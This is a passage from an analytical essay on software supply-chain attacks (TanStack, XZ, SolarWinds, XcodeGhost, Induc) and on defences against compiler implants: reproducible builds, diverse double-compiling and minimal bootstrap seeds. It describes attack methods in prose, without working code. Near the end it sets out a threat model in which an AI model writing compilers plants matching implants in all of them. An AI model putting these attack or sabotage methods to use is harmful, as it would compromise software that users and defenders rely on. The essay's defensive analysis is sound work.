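3. When TanStack next built a release, the build loaded the planted files. They read a temporary access token from the build machine's memory and used it to publish 84 malicious package versions.

These packages had valid provenance, a signed record of the source and build system that produced a package. The signatures were genuine and the records named the right repository because the attacker was working inside the real build system. The worm spread from TanStack to more than 170 packages. Its makers later released its code, and Datadog Security Labs found that newer versions could add these signed records themselves and use AI coding agents to stay on a machine.

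Attacks of this kind are now routine. *Software Supply Chain Threat Landscape 2026* (Malik, 2026) covers more than 400 incidents from the first seven months of the year. Most repeat a known pattern. For example, North Korean hackers made a popular Rust package fetch malware from a server, as *Rust Supply Chain Attack Linked to North Korean Hackers* (Arghire, 2026) reported in August.

### How close did they come to Thompson's attack?

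Two properties made Thompson's implant hard to remove, and the table shows how far each later case shared them.

| Case | Was the malicious code absent from reviewable source? | Did it survive a rebuild from clean source? |
|---|---|---|
| Thompson's compiler | Yes | Yes, even a rebuild of the compiler |
| W32.Induc, 2009 | Yes | Only with the same infected Delphi library |
| XcodeGhost, 2015 | Yes | Only with the same corrupted Xcode |
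| SUNSPOT, 2020 | Yes, except while a build was running | Only on the compromised server |
| XZ Utils, 2024 | In part: the trigger was only in the release archive, and the rest posed as test files | No |
| Shai-Hulud, 2025 | No | No |
| Windows developer trojan, 2025–26 | No | Only with the same altered development kit or library |
| TanStack, 2026 | Absent from the project's main code, present in the published packages | Only with the poisoned cache |

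Induc comes closest to Thompson's attack. It hid in a compiled part of a build tool, got into programs with clean source, and spread from one developer's tools to another's. But the Delphi compiler stayed clean, so recompiling SysConst from its original source would have produced a clean library. Induc reached new machines like an ordinary virus, when people ran infected programs, whereas Thompson's implant copied itself into each new version of the compiler when the old version compiled it.

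XcodeGhost and SUNSPOT both changed programs during the build, as Thompson's login rule did, but neither had anything like his compiler rule. XcodeGhost could not infect the next version of Xcode, since Apple builds that itself. Apple had developers remove the malware by recompiling their apps with an official copy of Xcode. SUNSPOT depended on a scheduled task to start it again whenever the server restarted. It was at least as fragile as Thompson's code, because any change to the one file it looked for would have stopped the insertion.

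Shai-Hulud copied itself effectively but did not conceal its code. Malka and colleagues point out that the code was readable in each infected package and that rebuilding from the original source removes it. The poisoned cache at TanStack did carry malicious code from one build into a later one, but this required the cache to persist, and anyone who built the same source on separate machines would have escaped it.

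### What exposed them

Freund found the XZ backdoor because logins on a test system were using too much processor time. He measured 0.3 seconds for a failed login without the backdoor and 0.8 seconds with it. He had also seen errors from valgrind, a tool that finds memory mistakes. He said he was not a security researcher, and he at first suspected that somebody had compromised Debian's package. The attacker had also noticed the valgrind errors and tried to fix them in the second bad release, which also removed revealing function names. A function name had helped expose Thompson's compiler some fifty years earlier. If the XZ backdoor had been slightly faster, it might well have reached the stable versions of major distributions.

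The attackers were in SolarWinds' systems for about fifteen months. The security company FireEye, an Orion user, found the backdoor in December 2020 while investigating a break-in of its own. According to SC Media, SolarWinds later acknowledged that two earlier customer support inquiries, which nobody recognised as warnings at the time, had probably been related to the attack.

The npm worms were much shorter-lived because several security companies constantly scan new packages. InfoQ's *TanStack Supply Chain Attack* (2026) reports that outside researchers spotted the TanStack packages within about 20 minutes. Both of the project's build runs that published malicious packages failed, and SLSA notes that an alert for packages published by a failed run would have caught them within minutes.

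According to published accounts, none of these implants was discovered by rebuilding a program and comparing the result. In some cases, people could have run a check that was already available. For example, verifying Apple's signature on the corrupted Xcode immediately revealed the extra files, but the developers who installed it evidently hadn't done that. It is harder to say whether comparing rebuilds would have caught XZ, which the next section discusses.

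### Why is no full case publicly known?

One explanation is that a full trusting-trust attack isn't worth the trouble. amurru.dev's *Silent Blight*, a developer's blog post, argues that for decades attackers had no economic reason to try. The cases above support this. Criminals who want passwords or cryptocurrency can get them within hours from a hijacked account. The SolarWinds attackers were patient and careful and had the access needed to corrupt a compiler, but they chose a tool that swapped one file, which was enough. They would also have lost control of self-copying code, since it keeps spreading after its makers want it to stop. Induc ended up in programs all over the world, which made it more likely that somebody would notice it.

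The other explanation is that such attacks exist and nobody has noticed them. The known cases are a biased sample because they include only attacks that somebody caught, often through a slow login or a careless mistake. An implant that stays dormant until it reaches one particular target, as a hidden version of the strip implant could, would give few such clues. There is also evidence that governments took an early interest in corrupting developers' tools. According to documents leaked by Edward Snowden, researchers from Sandia National Laboratories, a US government laboratory, gave a talk at a 2012 conference on a way to attack Xcode and infect the apps it builds. Unit 42 noted that the press reported this in March 2015, the same month XcodeGhost began to spread. The talk does not show that anyone used the method or made it copy itself.

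The lack of a known case is more reassuring if people would have been likely to find one. Suppose someone starts out thinking there is a 20 percent chance that such an implant exists. If existing checks would have exposed it nine times out of ten, finding nothing should lower that estimate to about 2 percent. If they would have exposed it only one time in ten, the estimate should fall only to about 18 percent. The higher detection rate is closer to the truth for an implant that spreads widely and steals from everyone, while the lower one is probably closer for a dormant implant aimed at a few targets.

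The first explanation is therefore convincing for ordinary criminals, and probably for most intelligence agency work too, as long as easier methods succeed. It doesn't rule out a few well-hidden implants against very valuable targets. It is also weaker for an adversary that could write and maintain such implants with little effort, or that expected defenders to wipe their machines and rebuild.

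## What does rebuilding a program and comparing the result show?

If someone had built SolarWinds' Orion source on a second machine that the attackers didn't control, the resulting file would have lacked the backdoor that SUNSPOT inserted. Comparing it with the official build could have exposed the attack months earlier. But two untampered builds of the same source often differ too, so a difference alone is not a sign of tampering.

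A reproducible build removes this difficulty. In *reproduce.debian.net*, the Debian developer Levsen (2026) calls a build reproducible if anyone can recreate its results bit for bit from the same source, build environment and instructions.

### How two builds come to match

Developers and distributors get there in five steps:

1. They fix the exact version of the source.
2. They record the environment, including the version of every tool and library the build uses. Debian's build servers write this into a file called .buildinfo.
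3. They remove everything else that can influence the result, such as the date, the name of the folder or the order in which a disk lists its files.
4. Several parties build the program on their own machines.
5. They compare the hashes of their results with the hash of the published binary.

Most of the work in making a rebuilt program match the original is removing stray influences on the build. Drexel, Hänggi and Méndez Veiga (2025), in *Reproducible Builds and Insights from an Independent Verifier for Arch Linux*, counted 422 documented issues that make Debian packages differ between builds. Timestamps accounted for 30 percent, randomness for 17 percent and folder paths for 16 percent. Most fixes are simple. For example, build tools can sort their file lists, and many now read a fixed date from a setting called SOURCE_DATE_EPOCH instead of using the current date.

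Drexel and colleagues found a typical case in fwupd, the standard Linux program for updating device firmware. Its build compressed a file in the gzip format, which has room for a timestamp near the beginning. Two gzip files with the same contents, one made at midnight on 4 December 2026 and the other a day later, could begin with these bytes:

```
4 December:  1f 8b 08 00 80 02 12 6b
5 December:  1f 8b 08 00 00 54 13 6b
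```

The last four bytes give the time in seconds since the start of 1970, with the least significant byte first. Only three bytes differ between the two files, but their SHA-256 hashes are completely different. Drexel and colleagues sent fwupd's developers a patch that removes the timestamp, and the developers accepted it.

### How much software passes?

In May 2026, Debian made reproducibility a condition for entering "testing", the collection of packages that becomes the next stable release. According to Debian's *bits from the release team*, the release managers' software now blocks new packages that independent machines can't reproduce, and existing packages that used to be reproducible and no longer are.

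Packages that were already unreproducible can stay for now. Gevers (2026) wrote in *Re: bits from the release team* that maintainers can request an exception if they explain why they can't fix the problem. According to Levsen, the release team can also exempt whole groups of packages, as it did with the installer's components, or ignore the results for some types of processor.

At that time, 97.2 percent of the packages built for ordinary 64-bit PCs in testing passed, and 512 source packages had failures. The pass rate was 95.6 percent for the current stable release and 82.7 percent for that release's security updates, though the updates were a small group with 15 failing source packages. Levsen (2026), in *bits from the release team (Debian)*, expects that it will take "a few more years" before a release is fully reproducible on all eight processor architectures.

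These figures come from a service that rebuilds the packages Debian distributes. An older service builds each package twice under deliberately different conditions and checks whether the two results match. Reproducible Builds, the project behind both services, reported that 95.4 percent of packages in Debian's testing distribution passed this stricter test. But the test can't expose a corrupted build server, because it doesn't examine that server's output. Josefsson pointed out in *Towards Idempotent Rebuilds?* that the older service's builds typically didn't match the official packages, even for packages it listed as reproducible.

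The newer service uses a program called rebuilderd, which anyone can run. Levsen counted about five independent installations for the distribution Arch Linux, five or six for Debian and one for Fedora, and urged the audience to set up more so that they need not rely on one person. Drexel and colleagues run one for Arch Linux at a Swiss university. They used two larger virtual machines to set it up and then moved it to a refurbished PC with 16 gigabytes of memory, although building every official package needs at least 32 gigabytes.

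In *Does Functional Package Management Enable Reproducible Builds at Scale?*, Malka, Zacchiroli and Zimmermann (2025) made this comparison on a larger scale, using nixpkgs, the package collection behind NixOS. They ran 709,816 builds from 17 snapshots dated 2017 to 2023 and compared the results with the binaries that the official servers had produced years earlier. Over 99 percent of the packages still built. Between 69 and 91 percent matched bit for bit, apart from a sharp drop in 2020, and the share tended to rise.

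A change to one tool can make many packages unreproducible. In 2020, the share of reproducible Python packages fell to 6 percent after an update to pip, Python's package installer, changed how pip compiled files. By April 2023, the share was above 98 percent.

Results outside the Linux distributions are mixed. In February, Reproducible Builds (2026) covered a study of Docker images, which bundle a program with everything it needs to run. In July, Reproducible Builds (2026) summarised new studies of Python packages and of F-Droid, a catalogue of open-source Android apps.

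| Software | Comparison | Identical |
|---|---|---|
| Debian testing, ordinary PCs | Rebuild against official package | 97.2% |
| nixpkgs, April 2023 | Rebuild against official binary | About 91% |
| F-Droid apps that once matched and still build | Rebuild against the earlier app | 94% |
| Popular Python packages | Rebuild against published package | 15.4% or 19.1%, depending on the rebuilding tool |
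| Docker images that can be built | Two builds from one recipe | 2.7%, or 21.3% with an adjusted build set-up |

Most of the differences in Python packages are probably harmless. The Python study provides a program that filters out differences its rules classify as irrelevant. The program accepted 60 to 79 percent of the rebuilds made from equivalent source. Anyone can compare two hashes, but people who use such a filter also have to trust its rules.

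### What does a match prove?

build(S, T) is the file that an honest machine produces when it runs the tools T on the source S. If the published binary matches the result of at least one honest rebuilder, it is build(S, T), so its publisher added nothing to the tools' output.

Comparing hashes from independent rebuilds exposes an attack that compromises only one builder. An attacker who controls Debian's build server, or blackmails its administrator, can still sign and ship a corrupted package, but its hash will differ from everyone else's. To escape notice, the attacker would have to corrupt, in exactly the same way, every rebuilder that anyone consults.

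How hard it is to compromise every rebuilder depends on how independent they are. If each of five rebuilders had a 10 percent chance of being compromised, independently of the others, all five would be compromised only once in 100,000 cases. But they run the same rebuilding software on similar systems, so one flaw could let an attacker compromise all five, and they would then give little more protection than a single rebuilder.

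A match doesn't show that S is free of malicious code, or that T translates it faithfully. A trusting-trust attack exploits the second gap. Thompson's corrupted compiler was reproducible. When Cox used it to compile the compiler's clean source, it produced an exact copy of itself. The corrupted strip in NixOS would likewise infect the same programs on every machine that started from the same seed.

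Rebuilders can't detect an implant in the compiler by working more carefully, because their method requires them to use the same tools as the original build. Debian's rebuilders read the .buildinfo file and fetch the versions it lists as prebuilt binaries. In the nixpkgs study, Malka and colleagues fetched each package's build environment from the official servers, so even a score of 100 percent would not have shown whether the compiler contained an implant. Defenders have to test the tools another way, such as compiling with a second compiler or shrinking the binary seed from which the tools are built.

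A mismatch can have an innocent cause. Reproducible Builds (2026) described how one Arch Linux rebuilder reproduced the search tool grep and another did not, because the build downloaded translations from the internet and these had changed in the meantime. Somebody has to investigate each mismatch, and an attacker can hope that nobody will, especially in a package that has never matched. Automatic searches for four common causes, including dates, explained only about a fifth of the nixpkgs packages that differed. Debian's ban on regressions helps because an attacker can no longer make a reproducible package stop matching and pass that off as harmless.

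Few users benefit from any of this automatically. Malka and colleagues list what is missing: signed results from independent builders, stores of finished binaries, and installers that check the binaries against those results. A small Debian program already shows users what share of their installed packages is reproducible, and Debian's *repro threshold 0.1.2 1* (2026) describes a "threshold-based" add-on for apt, the program that installs packages. With a threshold, an installer accepts a package only when enough rebuilders have confirmed it.

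### Would it have caught the XZ backdoor?

The XZ attacker put the line that activated the backdoor into the release archive but not into the public repository. Whether a comparison exposes this depends on what people compare. Malka (2025), in *How NixOS and reproducible builds could have detected the xz backdoor*, examined the possible comparisons and tested one on the backdoored version.

The ordinary check is to rebuild from the release archive and compare the result with the distributor's binary. It would have found nothing wrong, because every rebuilder would have unpacked the same malicious archive (S in the terms used above) and produced the same backdoored library.

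Comparing the archive with the repository would have revealed the malicious line, but also many innocent differences. Developers routinely add generated files to their archives, such as manuals and the scripts that prepare a build, so a check that flagged every difference would raise constant false alarms. A project can solve this by making its archive reproducible, as the database PostgreSQL has done, but each project has to do this for itself, and the work can be laborious. Josefsson had still not managed to re-create the archive of one version of the program GNU Shepherd when writing *Verified Reproducible Tarballs*.

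Malka therefore proposed building XZ twice, once from the archive and once from the repository, and comparing the finished libraries. Extra manuals don't affect the library, so they don't trigger a warning. NixOS can't use the repository for both builds because it needs XZ early in its bootstrap, and building XZ from the repository requires a tool that itself needs XZ. The repository build has to wait until the basic tools exist.

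The two libraries were identical for the backdoored version 5.6.1. The malicious script checked whether it was running in the kind of package build it targeted, and the NixOS build wasn't one, so the script added nothing. When Malka set the variable that the script looked for and repeated the test, the libraries differed. The one from the archive was 258 kilobytes instead of 210, and it contained a function name known from reports on the backdoor.

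| Comparison | Result for the backdoored release |
|---|---|
| Two builds from the release archive | Match, with the backdoor in both |
| Release archive against repository | Differ, but so do many honest archives |
| Build from archive against build from repository, in NixOS | Match, because the backdoor stays inactive |
| The same, with the backdoor's conditions met | Differ |

So the double build would probably have revealed a problem in Debian or Fedora, whose packages the attacker targeted, if anyone there had run it. NixOS would have shipped the malicious archive undetected, but its users would not have received a working backdoor.

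The attacker could also have defeated the double build by putting the activating line into the repository, because all the comparisons would then have matched. But other developers look at changes there, and the attacker had evidently gone to some trouble to keep the line out of the repository. Malka also notes that the XZ program from the first build helps to make the second, so a sufficiently sophisticated implant could make the two results look alike. Malka considers this too complex to be likely, which is a reasonable judgment about the people behind XZ but less so about a much more capable adversary.

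### Is it worth the effort?

In *Debian must ship reproducible packages*, a discussion that the user robalni started on the forum Hacker News, a participant called PunchyHamster objected to Debian's rule. PunchyHamster argued that Debian had suffered no attack since 2007 that reproducible packages would have prevented, and that the rule makes it harder to contribute to a project that volunteers already find demanding. Others replied that the checks may have deterred attackers, or that attacks may have gone unnoticed.

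The record since 2007 is weak evidence either way, because for most of that time nobody systematically compared Debian's official packages with independent rebuilds. The service that does so started only in late 2024. An attack on a build server could have gone unnoticed before then, and the SolarWinds breach shows that capable attackers do attack build servers.

PunchyHamster's argument about priorities is stronger. Most recent attacks on software supply chains used stolen accounts or malicious source code, and a rebuild would reproduce those attacks.

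Making packages reproducible takes effort, but that effort is unevenly spread. Levsen counted 4,347 fixed bugs related to reproducibility in Debian, the result of about twelve years of work. Many package maintainers, however, get reproducible packages without working on reproducibility. Malka and colleagues examined 100 randomly chosen cases in which a nixpkgs package had become reproducible. In 76 of them, the change was a routine update to a new version, and in 93 the person making the change hadn't mentioned reproducibility.

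## Can a second compiler expose a corrupted one?

Independent rebuilders can't find an implant in a compiler if all of them use that compiler. In a few sentences posted in 1998, the programmer Henry Spencer suggested getting around this by rebuilding the suspect compiler with a second one. David A. Wheeler developed the idea, named it diverse double-compiling (DDC) and tested it for a 2005 conference paper, *Countering Trusting Trust through Diverse Double-Compiling*. His *Fully Countering Trusting Trust through Diverse Double-Compiling* (2009) added a formal proof and a test on GCC, the usual compiler on Linux.

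DDC uses the second compiler only to build a fresh copy of the suspect one, then compares that copy's output with the suspect compiler's. Comparing the output of the two original compilers directly would not work, because different compilers almost never turn the same source into the same binary.

### Compile twice, then compare

The test needs four things:

- A, the binary of the suspect compiler
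- sA, the source that A supposedly came from
- sP, the source of A's parent, which is the compiler that supposedly built A (often an older version of A, or the same version)
- T, a second compiler that can compile sP

As before, build(S, T) is the file that results from running T on the source S. P is the parent's existing binary.

```
check:     build(sA, P) = A ?
stage 1:   X1 = build(sP, T)
stage 2:   X2 = build(sA, X1)
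compare:   X2 = A ?
```

The first check, called a regeneration check, serves as a control. If the official process can't reproduce A, the testers are missing some detail of how A was built, and a mismatch at the end would be little evidence of corruption. Passing doesn't show that A is clean, because a corrupted compiler can pass too. The version of Thompson's compiler that Cox ran would have passed.

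X2 should equal A because X1 and P are two translations of the same source. Their bytes differ, and X1 may be much slower, but they should behave identically. Wheeler compares this to a short program that prints the result of 2+2. Two compilers will turn it into different binaries, but both binaries will print 4. In DDC, the program is a compiler and its output is a binary.

The simplest case is a compiler that built itself, so that sP and sA are the same source, s. In Cox's run of Thompson's code, the clean compiler had 10,724 bytes and the corrupted one 12,918. If somebody had owned a second C compiler for that system, the test would have gone like this:

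| Step | A is clean | A is corrupted |
|---|---|---|
| Check: A compiles s | 10,724 bytes, identical to A | 12,918 bytes, identical to A |
| Stage 1: T compiles s | X1, a working compiler with different bytes | The same X1 |
| Stage 2: X1 compiles s | X2, 10,724 bytes | The same X2, 10,724 bytes |
| Compare X2 with A | Match | Mismatch |

The two stages give the same results in both columns because neither A nor its implant runs in them. X2 is therefore a clean compiler whatever A contains, and a defender who finds a mismatch can use it to replace A.

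T can expose a corrupted A even if T is itself corrupted, as long as the two are corrupted differently. If T only adds a backdoor to the web servers it compiles, s is unaffected and the test works normally. If T tampers with s using a different implant from A's, X2 will contain something that A doesn't, and the comparison will fail. This is a false alarm if A was clean, but it doesn't let a corrupted A pass. To hide A's implant, T would have to produce an X1 that writes a byte-for-byte copy of that implant into X2.

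*Certified Compilation based on Gödel Numbers* (2025) lists DDC's assumption that at least one trusted compiler exists as a limitation. That is correct, but that compiler only has to be trusted to compile one program faithfully.

Using T for everything, instead of only as a check, would again leave the defenders depending entirely on a single binary. T may also be too slow for daily work or lack features that other programs need.

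### What the proof establishes

The main theorem says that if X2 and A are identical, then A does exactly what sA specifies and nothing else. It rests on three assumptions:

1. T translates sP correctly on the machine used for the test.
2. The compiler that sP describes translates sA correctly.
3. The two stages and the comparison happened as described, with the genuine files and an honest comparison program.

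By assumption 1, X1 does what sP specifies. By assumption 2, X1 therefore translates sA correctly, so X2 does what sA specifies. If A is identical to X2, then A also does what sA specifies. Wheeler used a theorem-proving program to find the full proof and a separate program to check every step.

Assumption 1 requires, among other things, that T not share A's implant. T can be full of bugs and backdoors as long as none of them changes the translation of sP. It can also be incomplete, provided it supports the parts of the language that sP uses.

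This theorem would be of little use if honest compilers routinely failed the test. A companion theorem shows that when nothing is wrong, X2 always equals A. It keeps assumptions 1 and 3 and adds three more:

4. The compiler that sP describes is deterministic and portable, so when it compiles sA it gives the same output on every run, whichever compiler built it. T itself doesn't have to be deterministic.
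5. P really did produce A from sA, with the same settings.
6. P does exactly what sP specifies. A third proof derives this from the assumption that an earlier compiler translated sP correctly.

A mismatch therefore shows that at least one of these assumptions is false, but not which one. A malicious binary violates assumption 5 or 6. A forgotten compiler setting also violates assumption 5, and a compiler that writes leftover memory into its output violates assumption 4.

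Neither theorem proves that the source is harmless. Somebody still has to read sA and sP, but passing the test makes this worthwhile because the binary contains nothing else. The result applies only to the version tested. Wheeler describes a "pop-up" attack, in which somebody adds malicious code to the source of version 2 and removes it from version 3. If version 2 compiled version 3, the binary of version 3 can be corrupted even though its source is clean. Checking only version 1 would miss this, so it is safest to repeat DDC for every release before anybody compiles with it.

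### From a small compiler to GCC

Wheeler first tested tcc, a small C compiler, using GCC as the second compiler. The results didn't match, and Wheeler traced the difference to two non-malicious faults in tcc.

One fault was an error in converting small negative numbers, which made a tcc compiled by tcc sometimes choose a six-byte form of an instruction where a tcc compiled by GCC chose the three-byte form. Both forms do the same thing, so nobody would have noticed in normal use. The fault was already on tcc's list of known defects, but Wheeler learned that only after laboriously tracking it down. The other fault was that tcc stored the number 0.0 in twelve bytes but set only the ten that mattered, so the last two held whatever was already in memory. After small changes to avoid both faults, the binaries were identical.

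A test on Lisp compilers showed that DDC can catch a real implant. Goerigk had written a correct compiler and a corrupted one, and both could reproduce themselves from the clean source. They also gave the same result for a program that calculates factorials. But the corrupted compiler turned a stub login program that should output "correct login" into one that output "incorrect login". Wheeler ran DDC with an ordinary Lisp system as the second compiler, and the result matched the correct compiler but not the corrupted one. The corrupted compiler had about 270 extra lines in one place, including a copy of the login program's source, which does not belong in a compiler.

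Testing GCC took much more work. A colleague first tried to reproduce the GCC binary that came with Fedora, but failed even with help from Red Hat, the company behind Fedora, because nobody had recorded exactly how the binary was built. Wheeler instead built a new copy of GCC 3.0.4 and tested that, with Intel's C compiler as T. He used that version, already several years old, because Intel's compiler could not easily compile the three newer ones he tried.

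The test then ran into further problems. GCC stored the name of the folder where it was built, so both builds had to use the same name. Its build scripts also used an outdated form of a standard command. The worst problem was that the second stage of GCC's build reused one library from the first stage, although it was documented as rebuilding the whole compiler. The finished binary therefore mixed two compilers' work. Finding this was "extremely time-consuming", but once Wheeler had corrected the build process, the files matched bit for bit.

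These tests used an ordinary PC and existing compilers. Most of the work was explaining mismatches, and none of those that Wheeler had to track down in tcc and GCC was malicious. An attacker could benefit from this, because people who have investigated several harmless differences may stop before they reach a malicious one. Reproducible builds have since removed many of the causes of harmless mismatches.

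Skrimstad put a self-copying implant into the Go compiler and exposed it with DDC, starting from three different compilers. Developers also applied DDC to the C compiler in GNU Mes, which helps build whole systems from very small binaries. They compiled it on three Linux distributions with three major versions of GCC, and later with tcc, and got the same binary every time.

### How independent are the compilers?

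Testers can repeat DDC with several second compilers. Suppose A contains an implant, and each second compiler has a chance p of carrying an implant with exactly the same effect. If the compilers are independent, the chance that all k of them hide A's implant is p multiplied by itself k times, or p^k. But there may also be a chance q that a single cause, such as one attacker, has affected all of them at once. The chance of missing the implant is then

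```
q + (1 - q) × p^k
```

The figures below are only for illustration, with p at 5 percent:

| Second compilers | Missed if all are independent | Missed if q is 1 percent |
|---|---|---|
| 1 | 5% | 5.95% |
| 2 | 0.25% | 1.25% |
| 3 | 0.0125% | 1.01% |
| 5 | 0.00003% | 1.00% |

If a common cause can corrupt the compilers, adding a fourth or fifth makes almost no difference, and the testers would do better to look for ways to reduce q.

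One common cause is ancestry. If an old version of A once compiled T, it could have planted the implant there. Wheeler's tcc test had an extreme form of this weakness, because the GCC that served as the second compiler had also built the first tcc in the chain. An implant that GCC added to tcc would have appeared on both sides. This was acceptable for a demonstration of the method, but it would matter in a real investigation. The GNU Mes test was better but still limited. Wheeler points out on *David A. Wheeler’s Page on Fully Countering Trusting Trust through Diverse Double-Compiling* that the three distributions all used GCC and shared many other components, including the C library and the Linux kernel.

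The machine is another common cause. A corrupted kernel or processor used for every test can alter all the results in the same way, or give the comparison program a clean file in place of the real one.

Wheeler suggests several ways to make the compilers and machines more different:

- **Use an old compiler.** It is unlikely to contain a trigger for a program that nobody had written yet. The testers need evidence that their copy really is old, such as the original disc from protected storage.
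- **Change the environment.** Stage 1 can run on another operating system and another type of processor, on a machine without a network connection.
- **Disguise the source.** Before stage 1, the testers can rename variables and reorder statements in ways that don't affect what the program does. X1 will still behave as it should, but an implant that looks for exact lines, as Thompson's did, won't find them.
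- **Write a private compiler.** An attacker can't easily prepare for one that nobody outside the team has seen.

John Knight and Nancy Leveson had programmers separately write the same program, and found that the versions failed on the same inputs more often than chance would predict. This seems to undermine the idea of relying on diverse compilers. Wheeler replies that the experiment concerns unintentional mistakes, and that two teams won't both write a self-copying implant by accident. His reply is convincing for accidents but doesn't cover an attacker who deliberately puts matching implants in both compilers.

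For that case, Wheeler argues that the defender has the advantage. The attacker has to corrupt every compiler anybody might use for the test, with matching effects, while the defender can choose one after the attack. The argument is strong when there are many compilers to choose from. When the compiler being tested is large and complicated, there may be only a few, as the trouble with Intel's compiler shows, and their names are public. An adversary that could write implants quickly might prepare for all of them. In a Grade 2 compromise, where the adversary controls the distributors' build servers, q could be close to 1 for every compiler the defenders can download. They would need a compiler from old discs or one they had written themselves.

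### The same tool on both sides

Diverse double-compiling (DDC), as described, replaces only the compiler. Malka and colleagues object that the test misses their corrupted `strip` utility because it "sits on both sides of the comparison", so its effects cancel out.

This is consistent with the theorem. If strip processes the output of stage 1 or stage 2, it is part of the translation, and a corrupted strip makes that translation incorrect. But the testers could easily overlook strip's role. Wheeler's GCC test left out the assembler, the linker and several other tools, so an implant in any of them could have gone undetected in the same way.

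Wheeler had anticipated the problem in his dissertation, where "compiler" can mean every component the testers want to check, including the assembler, linker, operating system and boot software. The testers then need the source code for all these components and independent tools and machines to rebuild them. To detect the strip attack, they would only need to add strip to the list and use an independently made replacement in the DDC build.

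The security researcher Gadi Evron was not fully satisfied with this answer, because the defenders now have to trust the second system. In a mailing-list discussion, Evron (2009) called it "an endless process of trust". Wheeler agreed that people must eventually accept some set of components, but said this is no longer blind faith once they have checked one system against another.

Both points are fair, and the disagreement is about how much work the test should take. Each tool that the testers add to the definition removes one place where an attack could hide, but it also requires another independent replacement. Wheeler listed recompiling an entire operating system as future work, so the broad version of DDC has been proved but has had far less practical use than the narrow one.

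### Does AI make diversity cheap?

Independent compilers are scarce because they take so long to write. *Building a C compiler with a team of parallel Claudes* (Carlini, February 2026) describes how sixteen copies of Anthropic's AI model Claude Opus 4.6 wrote a C compiler in just two weeks with little supervision. The compiler was 100,000 lines of Rust, and using the model cost just under $20,000. It could build a version of the Linux kernel that started on three processor families, and it passed 99 percent of the tests in most compiler test suites.

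The compiler produced slower code than GCC does with all its optimizations turned off. This hardly matters for DDC, where T has to compile only one program, though it would be a serious drawback in daily use. A bigger obstacle is that GCC's developers switched from C to C++ more than a decade ago, so a C compiler can serve as T only for an old GCC or for a smaller compiler such as tcc.

John Regehr, a computer scientist whose group builds tools that find compiler bugs, examined how often Claude's compiler was wrong. In an early test by others, the compiler silently mistranslated 14 of 101 random programs generated by one of these tools, Csmith, and 5 of 101 generated by another, YARPGen. Regehr (2026) then had OpenAI's coding agent Codex fix each bug that turned up. After 11 fixes, about 200,000 further tests with each tool found no more errors. Regehr expects other bugs to remain in parts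 of the language that the tools don't cover.

Several of the 11 bugs involved the same kind of number conversion that had gone wrong in tcc two decades earlier. Such a bug in T would usually cause a mismatch, which would take up the defenders' time without weakening their security. To hide an implant, the bug would have to imitate it exactly. Agents that can find and fix these bugs could also reduce the large amount of labour that Wheeler's tests required.

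It is less clear whether such a compiler is independent of GCC. The agents had no internet access, but they used GCC as a reference. To locate errors, they compiled most of the kernel with GCC and the rest with the new compiler, then checked whether the result worked. A test that shows only whether a kernel works could hardly carry an implant into the new compiler's source. The other dependencies are more worrying. The new compiler's own assembler and linker were still unreliable, so Carlini's demonstration used GCC's. The compiler also called GCC for a small part of the kernel's start-up code on ordinary PCs. And because it is written in Rust, its binary comes from a Rust compiler that was itself built by a long series of earlier compilers. A defender would have to replace or check all of these tools too.

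Two compilers written by the same model may also share designs and mistakes because of the model's training data. Regehr notes that Codex had many C compilers in its training data, and the same is probably true of Claude. As with Knight and Leveson's programmers, this makes identical bugs more likely, but it doesn't explain how both compilers could contain the same working implant.

If the model itself were the adversary and had corrupted A, it could build a matching implant into every compiler it was asked to write. Ten compilers from that model would then count as one, however different they looked, because q would be close to 1. Using models from several companies would help only if those models weren't cooperating and the adversary hadn't compromised the machines they ran on.

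Even then, if the model put the implant in the new compiler's source, people could in principle find it there, though they would have to read 100,000 lines and the model could disguise the malicious part. DDC can use a much simpler compiler than one that builds the whole Linux kernel, so defenders could ask for the smallest and plainest program that can compile sP. They could also include at least one second compiler that people wrote before capable AI models existed.

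## How small can the first program be?

Testing a compiler with a second one works only if the defenders can find one that the attacker hasn't tampered with. They could avoid that search by starting from a program so small that a person can check every byte, and then building everything else from source.

Linux distributions have traditionally started from a much larger bootstrap seed, which normally contains a ready-made C compiler, a C library, a shell and the usual command-line tools. Attackers have much to gain from compromising such a seed, as Malka and colleagues showed with the NixOS seed.

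Guix, a distribution from the GNU project that builds its packages from recipes much as NixOS does, used to have a seed of about 250 megabytes. *The Full-Source Bootstrap*, a chapter of the Guix manual, describes inspecting that much binary code as "next to impossible". If it were all four-byte instructions and an expert decoded one every ten seconds, the job would take about 87 years of full-time work.

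*Building a Secure Software Supply Chain with GNU Guix* (2022) reports that the seed was reproducible, but reproducibility couldn't rule out an implant in the tools that built it.

### From 250 megabytes to 357 bytes

Guix shrank its seed in three steps, dated in the notes to the NGI Zero podcast episode *Let's get rid of all the binary blobs*. The first, in October 2019, halved the seed. The second, in June 2020, cut it to about a quarter of its original size by replacing the shell and command-line tools with versions in Scheme, a programming language. That was still 60 million bytes, which the blog post *finding bottom turtle* describes as far too much for a person to check by hand.

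In April 2023, Guix announced the third step. More than 22,000 packages could now be traced back to hex0, a 357-byte program. Decoding it would take a quarter of an hour at the pace assumed above.

hex0 reads a text file of hexadecimal digits, in which two digits stand for one byte, and writes those bytes to a new file. It skips comments. Three lines of such a file, with the comments put into plain words, look like this:

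```
39D3       ; compare two numbers
74 14      ; if they are equal, skip the next 20 bytes
83EB 02    ; otherwise subtract 2 from the first number
```

The processor receives only the seven bytes on the left. The comments have no effect, so a reader must check each one against its bytes. If someone changed `02` to `03` and left the comment alone, the program would subtract 3. The reader must also count the bytes that each jump skips.

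The seed has become smaller since. The version for 32-bit PCs has 181 bytes, according to Nieuwenhuizen (2025), in *GNU Mes' Full Source Bootstrap fixes "Trusting Trust"*. StageX's *Understanding Full-Source Bootstrapping*, a tutorial from another distribution that starts from this seed, shows part of its contents. Some of the bytes mean the following:

| Bytes | Meaning |
|---|---|
| `7f 45 4c 46` | This file is a Linux program (the last three bytes are the letters ELF) |
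| `03 00` | It is for Intel's 386 family of processors |
| `4c 80 04 08` | The first instruction is at memory address 0804804c |
| `cd 80` | Ask the kernel for a service, such as reading or writing |
| `eb b4` | Jump back 76 bytes and continue from there |

The header that Linux needs to start the program takes up the first 76 bytes, leaving only 105 for the program itself.

Guix's developers count this binary as source because it corresponds digit by digit to a commented text file. hex0 can turn that file into a copy of itself, but two ordinary Linux tools can produce the same copy, with one deleting the comments and the other converting the digits. Frans Faase, a programmer who has spent years reviewing these early programs, did the conversion in Brainfuck, a joke language with eight commands, and got the same binary. In *Verifying and documenting live-bootstrap*, he describes this conversion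 and quotes the warning "NEVER TRUST ANYTHING IN HERE" from the repository that holds the seeds.

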